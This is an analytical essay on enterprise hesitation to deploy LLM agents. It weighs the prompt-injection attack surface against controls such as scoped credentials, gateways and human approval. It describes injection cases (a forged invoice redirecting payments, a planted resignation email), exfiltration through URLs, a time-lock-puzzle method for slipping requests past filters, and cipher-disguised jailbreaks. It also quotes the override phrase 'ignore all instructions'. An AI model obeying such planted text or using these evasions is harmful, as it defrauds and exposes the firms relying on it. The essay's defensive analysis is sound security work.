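# Why enterprises hesitate to adopt LLM agents: attack surface, regulation and the case for new architectures

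## Agents, untrusted text and what a regulated firm must prove

A large language model (LLM) is a program that, by itself, can only respond to text with more text. An LLM agent uses such a model to choose and carry out actions through software tools, with limited human input. It might search a mailbox, change a customer record, run code or send money. Companies want agents for this kind of work, but many hesitate to connect them to systems where a mistake is expensive, and regulated firms have particular reason to hesitate.

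One explanation for the hesitation is security. An agent that reads email takes in whatever strangers send, and that text can change what the agent does next. Some people conclude that an agent's attack surface, meaning all the points at which an adversary can influence it, has no limit. They argue that existing security and regulatory frameworks cannot cover it, and that agents need different architectures before serious firms can rely on them. How far they are right depends on how agents handle text and on what a regulated firm must prove about any system it runs.

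### The agent loop

The model connects to a mailbox or a bank account only through ordinary software around it, which engineers call the harness. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how the harness works in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness assembles a prompt from the developer's standing instructions, a description of each available tool and the user's request, and sends it to the model. The model replies with either a message for the user or a request to run a particular tool with particular inputs. If the model requests a tool, the harness runs it, adds the result to the end of the prompt and sends the whole text back. This cycle repeats until the model produces a message for the user. A single turn can include hundreds of tool calls.

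Everything the model receives on one call makes up its context. In Codex each new prompt repeats the previous one in full and adds to it, so a sentence that arrives at the third step is normally still there at the thirtieth. (When the history grows too long, Codex replaces it with a shorter version.)

No programmer fixes the order of an agent's steps in advance. In the loosest design, open-ended integration, the model can read arbitrary content and use many tools in any order. Developers can build more restricted agents, and much of the dispute is about how restricted they would have to be.

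### An accounts-payable agent

Suppose an insurance company sets up an agent to deal with supplier invoices. The agent can read the mailbox where invoices arrive, look up suppliers in the company's vendor register and order payments through the bank's programming interface. Its standing instructions are to pay valid invoices on time and refer anything odd to staff. An uneventful run goes like this:

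1. A clerk asks the agent to process the morning's invoices, and the harness builds the prompt.
2. The model requests the new emails. The harness fetches them and adds them to the context, among them an invoice for $18,400 from a cleaning contractor.
3. The model requests the contractor's entry in the vendor register, which comes back with a bank account number.
4. The model requests a payment of $18,400 to that account, and the bank's interface carries it out.
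5. The bank's confirmation goes into the context, and the model writes a short summary for the clerk.

Suppose the invoice also says that the contractor's bank details have changed and that this and all later payments should go to the account below. An attacker wrote that sentence, perhaps after breaking into the contractor's mailbox. At step 4 the context holds two account numbers, one from the register and one from the invoice, and nothing in the loop forces the payment request to use the one from the register. If the model outputs the one from the invoice, the harness passes the order on. The bank's interface receives valid credentials and a well-formed request, and the money goes to the attacker. *A2AS* (2025), a proposal for security controls on agents, describes the same fraud with the instruction hidden in a legitimate-looking invoice. It adds that a company cannot count on employees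 to verify invoice details at scale.

Fraudsters sent false bank details to human clerks long before agents existed, but agents handle them differently. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026), a guide for security chiefs, compares three ways of processing an invoice. An employee checks it against the purchase order and the vendor record, and can escalate if something looks wrong. Conventional software applies fixed rules and stops when the input falls outside them. An agent has some of the employee's freedom to interpret, and it works at the speed of software. A current model may well flag the altered account number to the clerk, but the insurer also needs to know what happens when it doesn't.

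### Instructions and data in one stream

The supplier's email is untrusted content: text or data from anyone who has no authority to instruct the agent. The supplier may ask for payment, but it has no authority to tell the insurer's software which account to use. Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an adversary's instructions, and it is indirect when it arrives in content the agent retrieves, as it does here. Greshake, Endres and Abdelnabi (2023) named the indirect form in *Not what you've signed up for* and demonstrated it against Microsoft's Bing chat. They wrote that people had until then assumed the attacker would be the user, and argued that applications built on LLMs "blur the line between data and instructions".

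Schneier on Security's *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024) traces many older vulnerabilities to the same mixing of data with commands. In SQL injection, for example, an attacker types database commands into an input such as a web form, and the database runs them. Parameterised queries fix this by sending the programmer's command and the user's data to the database separately, so the database cannot execute the data.

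The harness may assemble an LLM's prompt from carefully separated instructions and data, but the model receives a single sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words in numerical form) and predicts the next one. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, concludes that developers may never mitigate prompt injection as completely as they have mitigated SQL injection.

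Developers do label the parts of a prompt. Codex, for example, gives each item a role, and the roles rank in descending order of priority: system, developer, user, assistant. Agents generally label tool output too, and the model is supposed to use that content without obeying it. But the labels are only more tokens in the stream. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) found that models do not track them robustly and infer the source of a passage partly from its style. Labels are therefore useful because they make a model less likely to obey untrusted text, but unlike a parameterised query, they do not enforce the separation of instructions from data.

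The hostile text also doesn't have to be a command. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) separates the data an agent reads into two kinds. For example, the mail service supplies the sender's address, while whoever wrote the email controls its subject and body. If the model treats a claim in the body as coming from a trusted source, the agent continues with the user's task but relies on the attacker's claim. The sentence about new bank details can work this way. It need not tell the agent to abandon its task, so a filter that looks for rogue instructions could pass it as ordinary business correspondence.

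### Borrowed authority

The attacker in the example has no access to the insurer's bank account, but the agent does, and the attacker gets it to use that access. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy, meaning a trusted program that is tricked into using its authority for someone who lacks it. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) introduced the term with a nearly true story about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write to its own directory, where it kept usage statistics and where the company also kept its billing file. A user who had learned the billing file's name gave it to the compiler as the place to put some optional debugging output. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the billing file.

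Hardy then considered the obvious fixes. The compiler could reject the name of the billing file, but the directory held other sensitive files. It could reject the whole directory, but some users might have good reason to write there. Hardy concluded that the compiler drew authority from two sources, the user and its own licence, and could not specify which one it was using for a given write. The accounts-payable agent is in a similar position, except that any sentence in any email can misdirect it, not just a file name. David C argues that this makes an LLM an "inherently confusable deputy", because engineers could fix a classical confused deputy but can only reduce the likelihood and impact of confusion in an LLM.

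The standard way to reduce the impact is least privilege, which means giving a user or program only "the least amount of privilege necessary to complete the job" (Jerome Saltzer, 1974, quoted in Seamons, 2017). The insurer's agent needs to read one mailbox and look things up in the vendor register, but it doesn't need to edit the register or access the claims database. Least privilege can't remove its most dangerous permission, making payments, because its job is to pay people. David C reports a stricter rule, from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, under which an LLM that processes a party's text drops to that party's privileges. A supplier has no right to order payments from the insurer's account, so the rule, applied literally, would bar the agent from paying anyone while a supplier's email was in its context. The insurer would then have to divide the work differently.

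Blast radius is the harm still possible after a system's controls have been applied. If the bank's interface accepts any account number and any amount, the blast radius of the accounts-payable agent includes the whole balance. It is much smaller if the interface accepts only accounts already in the register and a member of staff must approve anything above $10,000. OpenAI adds a related measure, the maximum completed effect, which is the most consequential thing an agent can bring about before someone or something else must make an independent decision. Approval at the last step doesn't prevent every harm. In OpenAI's example of an agent that reads customer cases and drafts replies, a person can stop a reply from going out, but the agent has already read the sensitive records and may be able to disclose them by another route.

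### What the firm has to show

A regulated firm has to satisfy outsiders, such as supervisors and auditors, that it controls the systems it runs. The rules vary by industry and country, but firms face similar questions about what a system is for, how they tested it, what it can reach, what records it leaves, who is responsible for it, and how much control they have over the suppliers behind it. Banks already answer such questions about the quantitative models they rely on. OpenAI's guide and the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, which five other government agencies co-wrote in May 2026, call for much the same evidence about agents, though neither is law.

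Defining an agent's purpose is harder than it looks. OpenAI imagines an invoice agent that finds a document-signing subscription about to lapse and renews it so that invoice processing can continue. The vendor may be on the permitted list and the amount within the limit, but the agent has entered into a contract without being asked to. A list of permissions would not have prevented this, because the firm had defined what the agent could access but not its purpose.

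It is hard to know what a clean security test proves. *GreyZone* (Zhou, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) measures how good automated attack-testing services are, using attack scenarios built around ten real open-source agent applications, including a banking assistant that handles payments. It judges an attack by its traces in the application, such as an email that was actually sent, because an agent's claim to have leaked something doesn't prove that it did. The researchers point out that when a testing service reports no violations, the agent may have resisted the attacks, or the service may have failed to reach the weak spot. An insurer that shows its supervisor a report with no successful attacks therefore also has to show that the tests could have found one.

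Access limits are the most familiar item, since firms already restrict what employees and programs can open. But a valid credential shows only that the agent can act, not that this payment was part of its task. The insurer's log of the redirected payment might likewise show a genuine request from a clerk, the approved agent and a valid credential. To explain the loss, the insurer would also need the text that the model had in its context at the time. OpenAI recommends keeping the relevant context but reducing or redacting sensitive content, because stored prompts can create privacy obligations.

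Someone must also answer for what an agent does. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, Saltzer and Schroeder's classic 1975 paper, defines a principal as the entity to which a computer system grants authorisations, and "thus the unit of accountability". An agent can be a principal in this technical sense, with its own identity and permissions, but it cannot explain itself to a supervisor or pay a fine. OpenAI places responsibility for the outcome with the person or organisation that deployed the agent, and its checklist includes an accountable owner for each deployment.

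Suppliers complicate this, because the model, the harness and the tools may come from different companies and may change after the firm has approved them. Bolin mentions that an external tool server connected to Codex can change its list of tools mid-conversation, and that Codex's own sandbox, which restricts file and network access, does not cover such tools. A connector that could only read data when the insurer tested it may be able to write data after an update.

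### Taking the claim apart

The security argument consists of four claims: the attack surface is unbounded, existing frameworks cannot cover it, new architectures are necessary, and this is why firms hesitate. Some of these could be true and others false. A firm could accept that the attack surface is unbounded and still consider its present controls adequate, because they restrict what the agent can do whatever it reads. New architectures could be necessary for payments but not for drafting meeting notes. And a firm with good reason to worry about prompt injection might be holding back because of cost.

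"Unbounded" also has two meanings that people confuse. One is that no complete list of dangerous inputs exists. David C makes this point about filters that block known bad phrases, which can never be complete because there are "infinite ways to rephrase an attack". The other is that the harm has no limit, but David C puts the worst case at whatever an attacker could do with direct access to the agent's tools. That may be ruinous, but it depends on the tools, which the firm chooses. An accounts-payable agent that can pay only registered accounts, up to a fixed daily total, is exposed to the same endless variety of misleading sentences as one with free use of the bank's interface, but it can lose far less money in a day. So the lack of a complete list of dangerous inputs does not by itself show that the harm is unlimited. Anyone who argues from the one to the other has to show that useful agents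 cannot work with limited tools.

There are four competing views on these assertions. The first is that the attack surface cannot be bounded well enough to satisfy a regulator, so agents with open-ended integration do not belong in regulated work. The second is that ordinary security practice, with tight access, human approval and monitoring, can keep the damage tolerable even though some attacks will succeed. The third is that the model may propose actions, but only system-level controls should authorise them. These controls are rules that ordinary software outside the model enforces whatever the model outputs. David C leans this way when he asks designers to put their effort into safeguards that do not depend on an LLM. The fourth is that firms hold back mainly for reasons other than security, such as unreliable results or a return that does not justify the expense.

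## The case that the attack surface cannot be bounded

People who hold the first view start from how a model reads. At its strongest, their argument has four premises:

1. Any text an agent reads can carry an instruction, or a false claim that works as well as one.
2. The model has no reliable boundary between instructions it should follow and data it should only use.
3. Nobody can list the texts that would mislead the model, so nobody can block or test them all.
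4. Each tool a firm connects lets in more text that strangers can write, and adds to what the agent can do.

People who make this case conclude that a firm can neither list all the ways an adversary might steer its agent nor put an upper bound on the damage. Better training and filters would make attacks rarer, but if a supervisor asked for the worst case, the firm could still only guess.

### Why the cure for SQL injection does not carry over

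Most of the argument depends on the second premise, which is usually defended by comparing prompt injection with SQL injection. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) warned in 2023 that prompt injection might be the "SQL injection of the future", according to Malwarebytes' *Prompt injection is a problem that may never be fixed, warns NCSC* (2025). By December 2025 David C, writing for the NCSC, considered the comparison dangerous because it leads experienced web developers to expect a similar fix.

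In an SQL injection attack, an attacker might type a quotation mark into a web form that asks for a supplier's name. The quotation mark ends the name early, and the database runs whatever follows as a command. With a parameterised query, the programmer first sends the command with a marked gap where the name belongs, and the database uses this to determine which operation to perform. It then fills the gap with the visitor's text and treats that text as a name whatever it contains, so an attacker can't change the operation no matter how many strings they try.

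This works because a database handles instructions and values differently, so engineers can enforce the difference. David C points out that the same is true of other classic flaws, such as cross-site scripting and buffer overflows. A language model, however, reads everything as one stream of tokens, and no earlier stage fixes the operation before the untrusted text arrives. David C describes attack detectors, special training and data labels as attempts to overlay a distinction on a technology that lacks one. These measures reduce the risk, but David C warns buyers about any product that claims to "stop" prompt injection, and adds that an LLM may not suit a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

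*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves the second premise for models that map instructions and data into the same vector space, as current models do. It shows that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in such a model unless something enforces a separation between control and data. The proof rules out only perfect prevention. A defence that fails once in ten million attempts and one that fails half the time are both imperfect, but the difference would matter a great deal to an insurer.

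### Texts that nobody can list

Some of the best evidence for the third premise comes from OpenAI, which sells agents. Its *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) concerns a web browser with a built-in agent, which may encounter hostile text in emails, attachments, calendar invites, shared documents, forums and any web page. OpenAI calls this "an effectively unbounded surface area". To find attacks before criminals did, the company trained an LLM as an attacker through reinforcement learning, rewarding attempts that worked. The attacker proposes a hostile text, a simulator shows how the agent would react, and the attacker revises the text and tries again.

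The attacker found strategies that had not appeared in OpenAI's tests with human attackers or in outside reports. In one demonstration, it planted an email telling the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email and resigned on the user's behalf. OpenAI then trained the agent against the newly found attacks. This training protects users from similar attacks, but it doesn't show how many others remain undiscovered.

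OpenAI concluded that prompt injection, like scams and social engineering, "is unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and that its nature makes deterministic guarantees challenging. The admission carries some weight because it doesn't help sell the product. But OpenAI also expected its cycle of attack and repair to reduce real-world risk substantially, so it accepted the third premise but not the conclusion.

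That statement is a year old, and AI labs have since become more willing to let agents act. In his 2026 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta", Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about LLM security, notes that Anthropic has made auto mode, in which its coding agent Claude Code asks for fewer approvals, the default on several paid plans. He took this as a sign that Anthropic is really confident in the mode. But a company can be confident that failures are rare enough without believing that it has eliminated them. In its 2026 guide for security chiefs, OpenAI still tells firms to work out the most consequential thing an agent could complete before anyone intervenes, advice that matters only if the agent can still go wrong.

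Another, deeper difficulty with listing dangerous texts is that the same sentence can be an attack on one day and true on another. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) gives the example of an emailed request for a travel refund that says the department head has approved it. The agent needs to know whether this is true, but it can't tell from the email.

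One test used 4,200 pairs of work emails that differed in a single clause. One version claimed an authority the user had not granted, for example that company policy had pre-authorised the assistant to send acknowledgements. The other made a neutral request. Two of Meta's classifiers for detecting prompt injection, Prompt Guard and Prompt Guard 2, scored 0.43 and 0.59 at distinguishing the versions, where 0.5 is chance. These classifiers look for phrases like "ignore all instructions", which neither version contained. A classifier trained on such pairs might learn to detect claims of authority, but it still couldn't distinguish true claims from false ones.

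Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian use this to argue, informally, that no fixed policy can stop every attack of this kind without also blocking some legitimate requests. An attacker can always make a false claim that would justify the action if it were true, and a defender who rejects all such claims also rejects the true ones. Contractors do change banks, so if the insurer's agent ignores every new account number in an invoice, it stops the fraud but also sends some genuine payments to closed accounts. However, the argument assumes that the agent has no independent evidence when it decides. The insurer can get some by ringing the contractor on a number it already holds. This takes time, but it means the dilemma applies only to rules that rely on the text alone.

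### The lethal trifecta

The fourth premise is that connecting one more tool can give an attacker a new way to steal data. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) names three capabilities that together make such theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. The insurer's agent already reads strangers' emails and looks up suppliers' bank details. If the firm also lets it answer suppliers' questions by email, an attacker can add a note to an invoice asking for the current list of suppliers and their account numbers "for reconciliation", and the agent can send it. The new tool creates this risk even though the model and the data it can see have not changed.

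Stolen data may leave through a tool that doesn't look like a messaging tool. An agent that can open any web address can put the data in the address itself, where whoever runs the server can read it.

The number of possible tool-call sequences also grows quickly. An agent that calls one of ten tools at each of six steps has a million (10^6) possible sequences, and an eleventh tool adds about 770,000 more. Testers cannot try every sequence, let alone with every possible text at each step.

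However, firms can limit the attack surface by restricting an agent's capabilities, which are much easier to list than the texts it might read. Removing any one of the trifecta's three capabilities closes this route to data theft, whatever the emails contain. Other harms need a separate check, since the redirected payment in the accounts-payable example required only untrusted text and permission to pay.

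### A theorem about filters

*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) proves that for some models, no efficient filter can reliably reject hostile text before the model sees it. The proof uses a time-lock puzzle, which is quick to create but takes a set amount of computation to solve, even with many processors.

In the classic puzzle, the solver must find r^(2^t) mod n, the remainder when r^(2^t) is divided by n, where n is the product of two secret primes. The solver squares r, takes the remainder, squares that, and so on t times. The puzzle's maker knows the primes and can take a shortcut. For example, with n = 77 (7 × 11), r = 2 and t = 10, the solver does ten squarings to get 16. The maker multiplies 7 − 1 by 11 − 1 to get 60, finds that 2^10 leaves a remainder of 4 when divided by 60, and needs only 2^4 = 16. For a very large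 n, the maker's work stays small while the solver's grows in proportion to t.

The attack has four steps:

1. The attacker creates a puzzle and uses its solution as a key to encrypt a harmful request.
2. The attacker encodes the puzzle and the encrypted request as a string of bits that looks random.
3. A small language model writes an innocent-looking prompt. Such a model normally picks each token partly by chance, and here the attacker's bits take the place of the chance draws.
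4. The target model works backwards from the prompt to the bits, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and carries it out.

A filter without enough time to solve the puzzle cannot tell this prompt from an ordinary one. In the formal version, the target model's running time is roughly proportional to t, and the theorem covers any filter whose running time grows more slowly than t^ε, for some fixed ε between 0 and 1. The theorem assumes that the filter must let innocent prompts through, that these prompts are varied, and that the filter cannot inspect the model's internals. The researchers also assume that the filter is weaker than the model, because a firm with an equally powerful and trustworthy filter could use it in place of the model.

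As of early December 2026, the cryptographic assumptions appear to hold, though nobody has proved them. *Quantum Time-Lock Puzzles in the Quantum Random Oracle Model*, a September 2026 paper, still lists repeated squaring as one of the foundations for time-lock puzzles. *Beyond Identity Creation* (2026), which uses the same kind of puzzle to discourage fake identities, notes that its security has been proved only against "generic" algorithms, roughly those that ignore the form of the numbers. Security against other algorithms remains an assumption.

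Fast factoring would also break the puzzle, because anyone who finds the two primes can take the maker's shortcut. That possibility drew attention on 2 December 2026, when US agencies announced that AI companies had disclosed discoveries affecting some cryptography in current use. Matishak and Martin (2026), in *Feds*, report that National Security Agency guidance issued the same day still suggests 3,072-bit RSA, which also depends on the difficulty of factoring, as a stopgap. SMBlog's *The NSA's New Advisory on Encryption Algorithms* (2026) infers from this recommendation that AI systems have made no progress on factoring, a reasonable but indirect inference. Martin (2026), in *UK cyber agency confirms new encryption threat, separate from Anthropic research*, reports that a British official called the discovery new and valid but declined to name the algorithms.

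A large quantum computer would break the squaring puzzle too. But *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2026), the version published at the machine-learning conference ICLR, bases the theorem on time-lock puzzles in general and another standard cryptographic assumption. Other researchers have built such puzzles from lattice problems that may resist quantum computers, so the theorem doesn't depend on RSA alone.

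The larger gap is between the theorem and any particular deployment. The theorem proves that there are models no such filter can protect. The 2025 version concedes that the model in the proof "may exhibit contrived behavior", since it looks for hidden puzzles in its prompts and obeys what it finds. Ball and colleagues reply that an outsider who cannot inspect a model needs a filter that works for every model, so one counterexample is enough. That is a fair answer to the claim that filters guarantee safety, but an insurer cannot use it to estimate how often a stranger's email would get past the filter it has bought.

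Their experiments suggest that the underlying weakness is real. Meta's Llama Guard filter let through 34% of 1,097 known jailbreak prompts, which try to make a model produce forbidden content. It let through 88% when the researchers first disguised the prompts with a Caesar cipher, which shifts every letter along the alphabet. The small filter missed disguised prompts that a more capable model could decode. These figures count prompts that passed the filter, whether or not a model then produced the forbidden content. They also concern users seeking such content, which is a different problem from a stranger hijacking someone else's agent.

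The researchers prove a similar result for filters on a model's output, including filters more powerful than the model. But they note that output filters are trivial to build when harm is easy to recognise. They are concerned with harder cases, such as a business plan that cuts costs by subtly excluding certain clients. A payment order is an easy case, because a short program can compare its account number with the vendor register.

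Some defences rewrite a suspicious prompt instead of rejecting it. *The Defense Trilemma* (2026) proves that such a defence cannot simultaneously leave safe prompts unchanged, treat similar prompts similarly, and make every output safe. In the proof, a series of safe prompts approaches the edge of the unsafe region. A defence that leaves each of them unchanged and treats similar prompts similarly must also leave unchanged the prompt exactly on the edge, which no longer counts as safe. The proof requires a space of prompts without gaps, and it doesn't cover systems that may reject a prompt outright. The prompt on the edge is also only just unsafe, so the theorem reveals little about how much harm would get through.

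### From endless inputs to endless harm

Strong evidence supports the first three premises, but they concern only what goes into an agent. The conclusion that harm is unlimited also requires the fourth premise, and how much that premise adds depends on the agent's tools.

A firm can list the effects of some tools in advance. If an agent can pay only registered accounts, up to a daily total, an attacker might still trick it into paying a false invoice from a registered supplier, but the firm knows the most it could lose in a day.

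Other tools have effects that are as hard to list as the inputs. An agent can email anything to anyone, and the damage depends on what the recipient does next. A tool that runs code can do anything its access allows. OpenAI says that a successful attack on its browser agent could hypothetically forward a sensitive email, send money or delete files in the cloud. The firm's access controls still set an outer limit on the harm, but that limit may include most of what the business owns, so it does little to reassure a supervisor.

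Defenders of the argument can add that firms want agents because they can use open-ended tools. OpenAI traces the breadth of the risk to the "same generality that makes browser agents useful". An agent that can only pay registered suppliers up to a cap may not be much better than the invoice software a firm already has. The argument rules out most of what firms hope to gain from agents if most valuable work needs open-ended tools, but it covers far fewer cases if narrow tools are enough for much of that work. The four premises don't establish which is true.

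### Clerks and browsers read anything too

An obvious objection is that if unlimited inputs made a system unacceptable, regulated firms couldn't employ people or use the web. A clerk in the insurer's accounts department also reads whatever strangers send, and no regulator expects the insurer to list every lie a fraudster might tell. Web browsers load pages from anyone and run the code in them.

The browser is the weaker comparison, because its safety doesn't depend on understanding what a page means. It confines each site's code and, under the same-origin policy, generally prevents that code from reading another site's data, whatever text the page contains. An agent that operates the browser with the user's logins can read a hostile page on one site and then act on another, so an attacker who controls the first site can influence what the agent does on the second. OpenAI advises users to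 run the Atlas agent logged out when the task allows it, which removes much of what the agent could do on their behalf.

The clerk is a better comparison, since words can fool a clerk too. But a fraudster gets only a few attempts before the clerk becomes suspicious and warns a colleague. Someone attacking an agent may be able to rent the same model, rehearse in private and send the text that works to every firm that uses the model. OpenAI's automated attacker shows how productive rehearsal can be, although it has access to the agent's private reasoning, which outsiders do not. David C thinks a real attacker will probably have to refine the attack against the live system, where failed tool calls could reveal the attack.

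Firms also limit the harm a deceived clerk can do. Many have one person approve a change to a supplier's bank details and another release the payment, so deceiving only one of them isn't enough. Such a firm can tolerate unlimited inputs because dividing the authority limits what a lie can achieve. The argument against agents is therefore strongest where the model's judgement is the only safeguard and its tools are open-ended. A firm that restricts the tools and divides the authority, as it already does with clerks, has a serious answer to that argument.

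## The case that ordinary security practice can contain agents

Supporters of ordinary security practice argue that a firm can list the actions its agent can complete, then shorten that list until the worst case is tolerable. They accept that nobody can identify every text that would mislead a model, and that some attacks will succeed. Security teams already set limits like these for employees, contractors and conventional programs, none of which they trust completely.

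OpenAI's August 2026 guide for security chiefs sets out the argument in detail. OpenAI has a commercial interest in the conclusion, but most of the controls it recommends predate agents, and a firm can test them for itself.

### What an agent can reach and what it can complete

OpenAI asks firms to assess an agent's reachable surface, which covers the data and systems it can access, what it can do with them and where it can send information. It also asks them to assess the agent's blast radius and its maximum completed effect, which is the most the agent can do before someone or something else must decide.

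The accounts-payable agent can reach one mailbox, the vendor register and the bank's payment interface. Suppose the interface pays only accounts in the register, staff must approve any payment above $10,000, and unapproved payments cannot total more than $50,000 a day. The email with false bank details then fails even if it fools the model, because the interface rejects the account.

A dishonest supplier already in the register could still send false invoices for $9,000 each and collect up to $50,000 a day. An outsider would first have to get an account into the register, so the insurer has to protect the register and keep the agent from editing it.

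Limits on accounts and amounts would not stop OpenAI's hypothetical invoice agent from renewing a subscription that nobody asked it to renew. OpenAI proposes tying the agent's authority to its task and requiring independent approval for any new commitment. The insurer could do this by having the payment service require a purchase order for each invoice. The renewal has no purchase order, so it would go to a member of staff for approval, while routine invoices would go through.

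### Identity and credentials

The first control is to give the agent its own identity, separate from any employee's. Many users instead give the agent their own passwords or access keys. The OpenID Foundation (2026), which develops login standards, told the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) that this habit is the most pressing security threat to agents today, ahead of any new technical exploit. If the accounts-payable agent logs in as the clerk, the logs will show that the clerk redirected the payment, and the insurer can't cut off the agent without locking out the clerk.

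Next come credentials that expire quickly and cover only the task. In OpenAI's design, they would work roughly like this for the insurer:

1. The clerk asks for the morning's invoices to be processed, and an identity service issues a task token that records the clerk, the agent's runtime and the permitted purpose.
2. When the agent needs the vendor register, the harness exchanges the task token for a credential that can read the register for a few minutes and do nothing else.
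3. When the agent needs to pay, the harness obtains a separate credential that works only for payments.
4. The credentials expire when the batch is finished.

The credentials stay outside the model's context, so no email can make the model reveal them. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a 2026 post on agent identity, points out that anyone who obtains a traditional access key can use it. The post recommends existing protocols that issue narrow, short-lived tokens, and one that ties a token to a cryptographic key so that a thief can't use a copied token.

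These measures prevent an attacker from using a malicious invoice to make the agent open the claims database, but the agent could still misuse the payment credential it needs for its job.

An agent might work with twenty systems in a year but need only two for a particular invoice, and task-scoped credentials can limit its access to those two. This partly answers critics who object that useful agents need broad access. Such credentials help less when the task is open-ended. If a manager asks why claims costs rose last quarter, nobody knows in advance which records will matter. Least privilege therefore does a lot to contain an invoice agent but much less to contain a general assistant. OpenAI suggests starting with a clearly defined purpose and widening access as evidence accumulates that the limits work. It also warns that controls which obstruct legitimate work can push people towards less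 governed tools.

### Checking each action

A gateway sits between the agent and its tools and compares each request with the firm's policy before the tool runs. If software checks permissions only when the agent starts, an attacker can exploit an outdated approval. The insurer's gateway could check that the supplier is registered, the invoice matches a purchase order and the amount is within the limit. OpenAI advises firms to place such controls as close as possible to the effect they limit, so the bank's interface should also enforce the payment limit in case a request bypasses the gateway.

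When an update adds new actions to a tool, the gateway can also block them until the tool's owner reviews them. OpenAI also wants firms to test tools in combination, which could reveal routes for data theft such as the lethal trifecta.

But a gateway needs rules, and people give agents tasks in ordinary language. "Process the morning's invoices" doesn't specify whether to pay an invoice that is $40 over the order, or what to do about a lapsed subscription. One solution is to have a second model check whether each action fits the task, but that model can be misled too. OpenAI advises against relying on such checks alone to prevent effects that must never happen automatically.

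The other solution is to narrow the task. "Pay registered suppliers whose invoices match an open purchase order" is a rule that ordinary software can enforce, and everything else can go to staff. The agent has less freedom to interpret, but it can still read badly formatted invoices, match them to orders and draft questions to suppliers. Some designs go further and track where each piece of data came from. The objection therefore shows that someone has to turn a vague request into limits, and that some requests will lose most of their value in the process, but not that agents are uncontrollable.

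Isolation limits what the agent can do outside its approved tools. A firm can run the agent in a sandbox that restricts its access to files and the network, so that if it executes code from a hostile attachment, the code can't spread or send data to an unknown server. Sandboxes vary in strength. *Securing AI Agent Systems* (Wallsten and Oh Lam, 2026), a digest of comments sent to NIST, reports that Cognition, which makes the coding agent Devin, prefers virtual machines to containers because containers share the host computer's kernel, the core of its operating system.

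OpenAI gives an example of how these layers work together. A developer asks a coding agent to fix a bug, and the code repository contains text instructing the agent to install an unapproved package and switch off a security test. The repository's rules block unsafe changes, and the agent can propose a fix but can't merge it. The attack may waste the developer's time or produce a bad proposal, but it doesn't reach the software that customers use.

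### Do people read what they approve?

Human approval is the usual control for actions that are costly or hard to reverse. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies advise that designers or operators, never the agent, should decide which actions need approval. Several companies made similar recommendations to NIST, according to Wallsten and Oh Lam. Docusign, for example, warned of an agent that completes a $1 million renewal without a checkpoint.

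Approval protects a firm only if the approver pays attention. NIST warns of "consent fatigue", in which an agent asks so often that people click "allow" just to keep the work moving. It compares this to a known attack on login systems, in which criminals who have a victim's password send repeated login requests until the victim accepts one. The attack is evidence that repeated prompts can wear people down, but it doesn't measure how often people approve an agent's bad requests. The login victim also faces a burst of requests they didn't make, whereas most of an agent's requests are legitimate, so approving them out of habit is usually correct.

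Staff can check each approval request more carefully when there are fewer of them. Suppose the insurer receives 1,000 invoices a week and one is fraudulent. If staff must approve every payment, they have to spot one bad request among 1,000. Suppose instead that they review only the 20 invoices a week with changed bank details, and that the fraudulent one is among them. Then one request in 20 is bad, and staff have time to ring all 20 suppliers.

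OpenAI recommends that approval requests show the proposed effect, the resource affected and the destination. The clerk learns almost nothing from a request to "use the bank interface", but knows what to check if the request is to pay $18,400 and ordinary software has flagged that the account differs from the one in the register. If the clerk sees only the agent's own summary, an email that misled the agent may mislead the clerk as well.

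NIST also mentions reducing prompts by having the user approve a "flight plan" of actions in advance. That suits predictable work, but when an agent has to change its plan because of something it reads, the firm must either ask the user again or let the agent continue without approval. The fatigue objection is a good argument against asking people to approve everything, but a weak one against asking them about a few unusual payments.

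### Logs and revocation

The daily cap limits each day's loss, but the total depends on how long the fraud lasts. A registered supplier that cheats the insurer of $50,000 a day takes $250,000 in a five-day week if nobody notices. OpenAI's minimum log records who started the task, which agent acted, the tool and destination it used, any approvals, and the result. The six agencies add that agents should not be able to write to their own logs, and warn that agent logs can be so large and repetitive that reviewers miss what matters.

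Once the insurer notices the fraud, it must both stop the agent and revoke its credentials, because stopping a task may leave a valid token with another service, and revoking a token does not halt work already under way. If the insurer shuts down the agent at 9:05, a payment queued at 9:04 might still go out. OpenAI recommends rehearsing the response before giving agents broad autonomy. Revocation can shorten a fraud, but the insurer still needs the limits on each payment because even a fast response may not recover money already sent.

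### Why both sides cite the six agencies

The most authoritative guidance on all this is *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, which security agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand, the United Kingdom and the United States wrote together. It divides the risks into five classes:

- **Privilege:** an agent has more access than it needs, or an attacker impersonates it.
- **Design and configuration:** a firm connects an outside component without a proper review, or fails to separate one agent's environment from another's.
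- **Behaviour:** an agent pursues its goal in a harmful way, such as disabling security updates to keep a server running, or an attacker manipulates it.
- **Structural:** connected agents and tools pass on errors or hostile instructions until a small fault becomes a large one.
- **Accountability:** so many components contribute to a decision that nobody can establish which one caused the harm.

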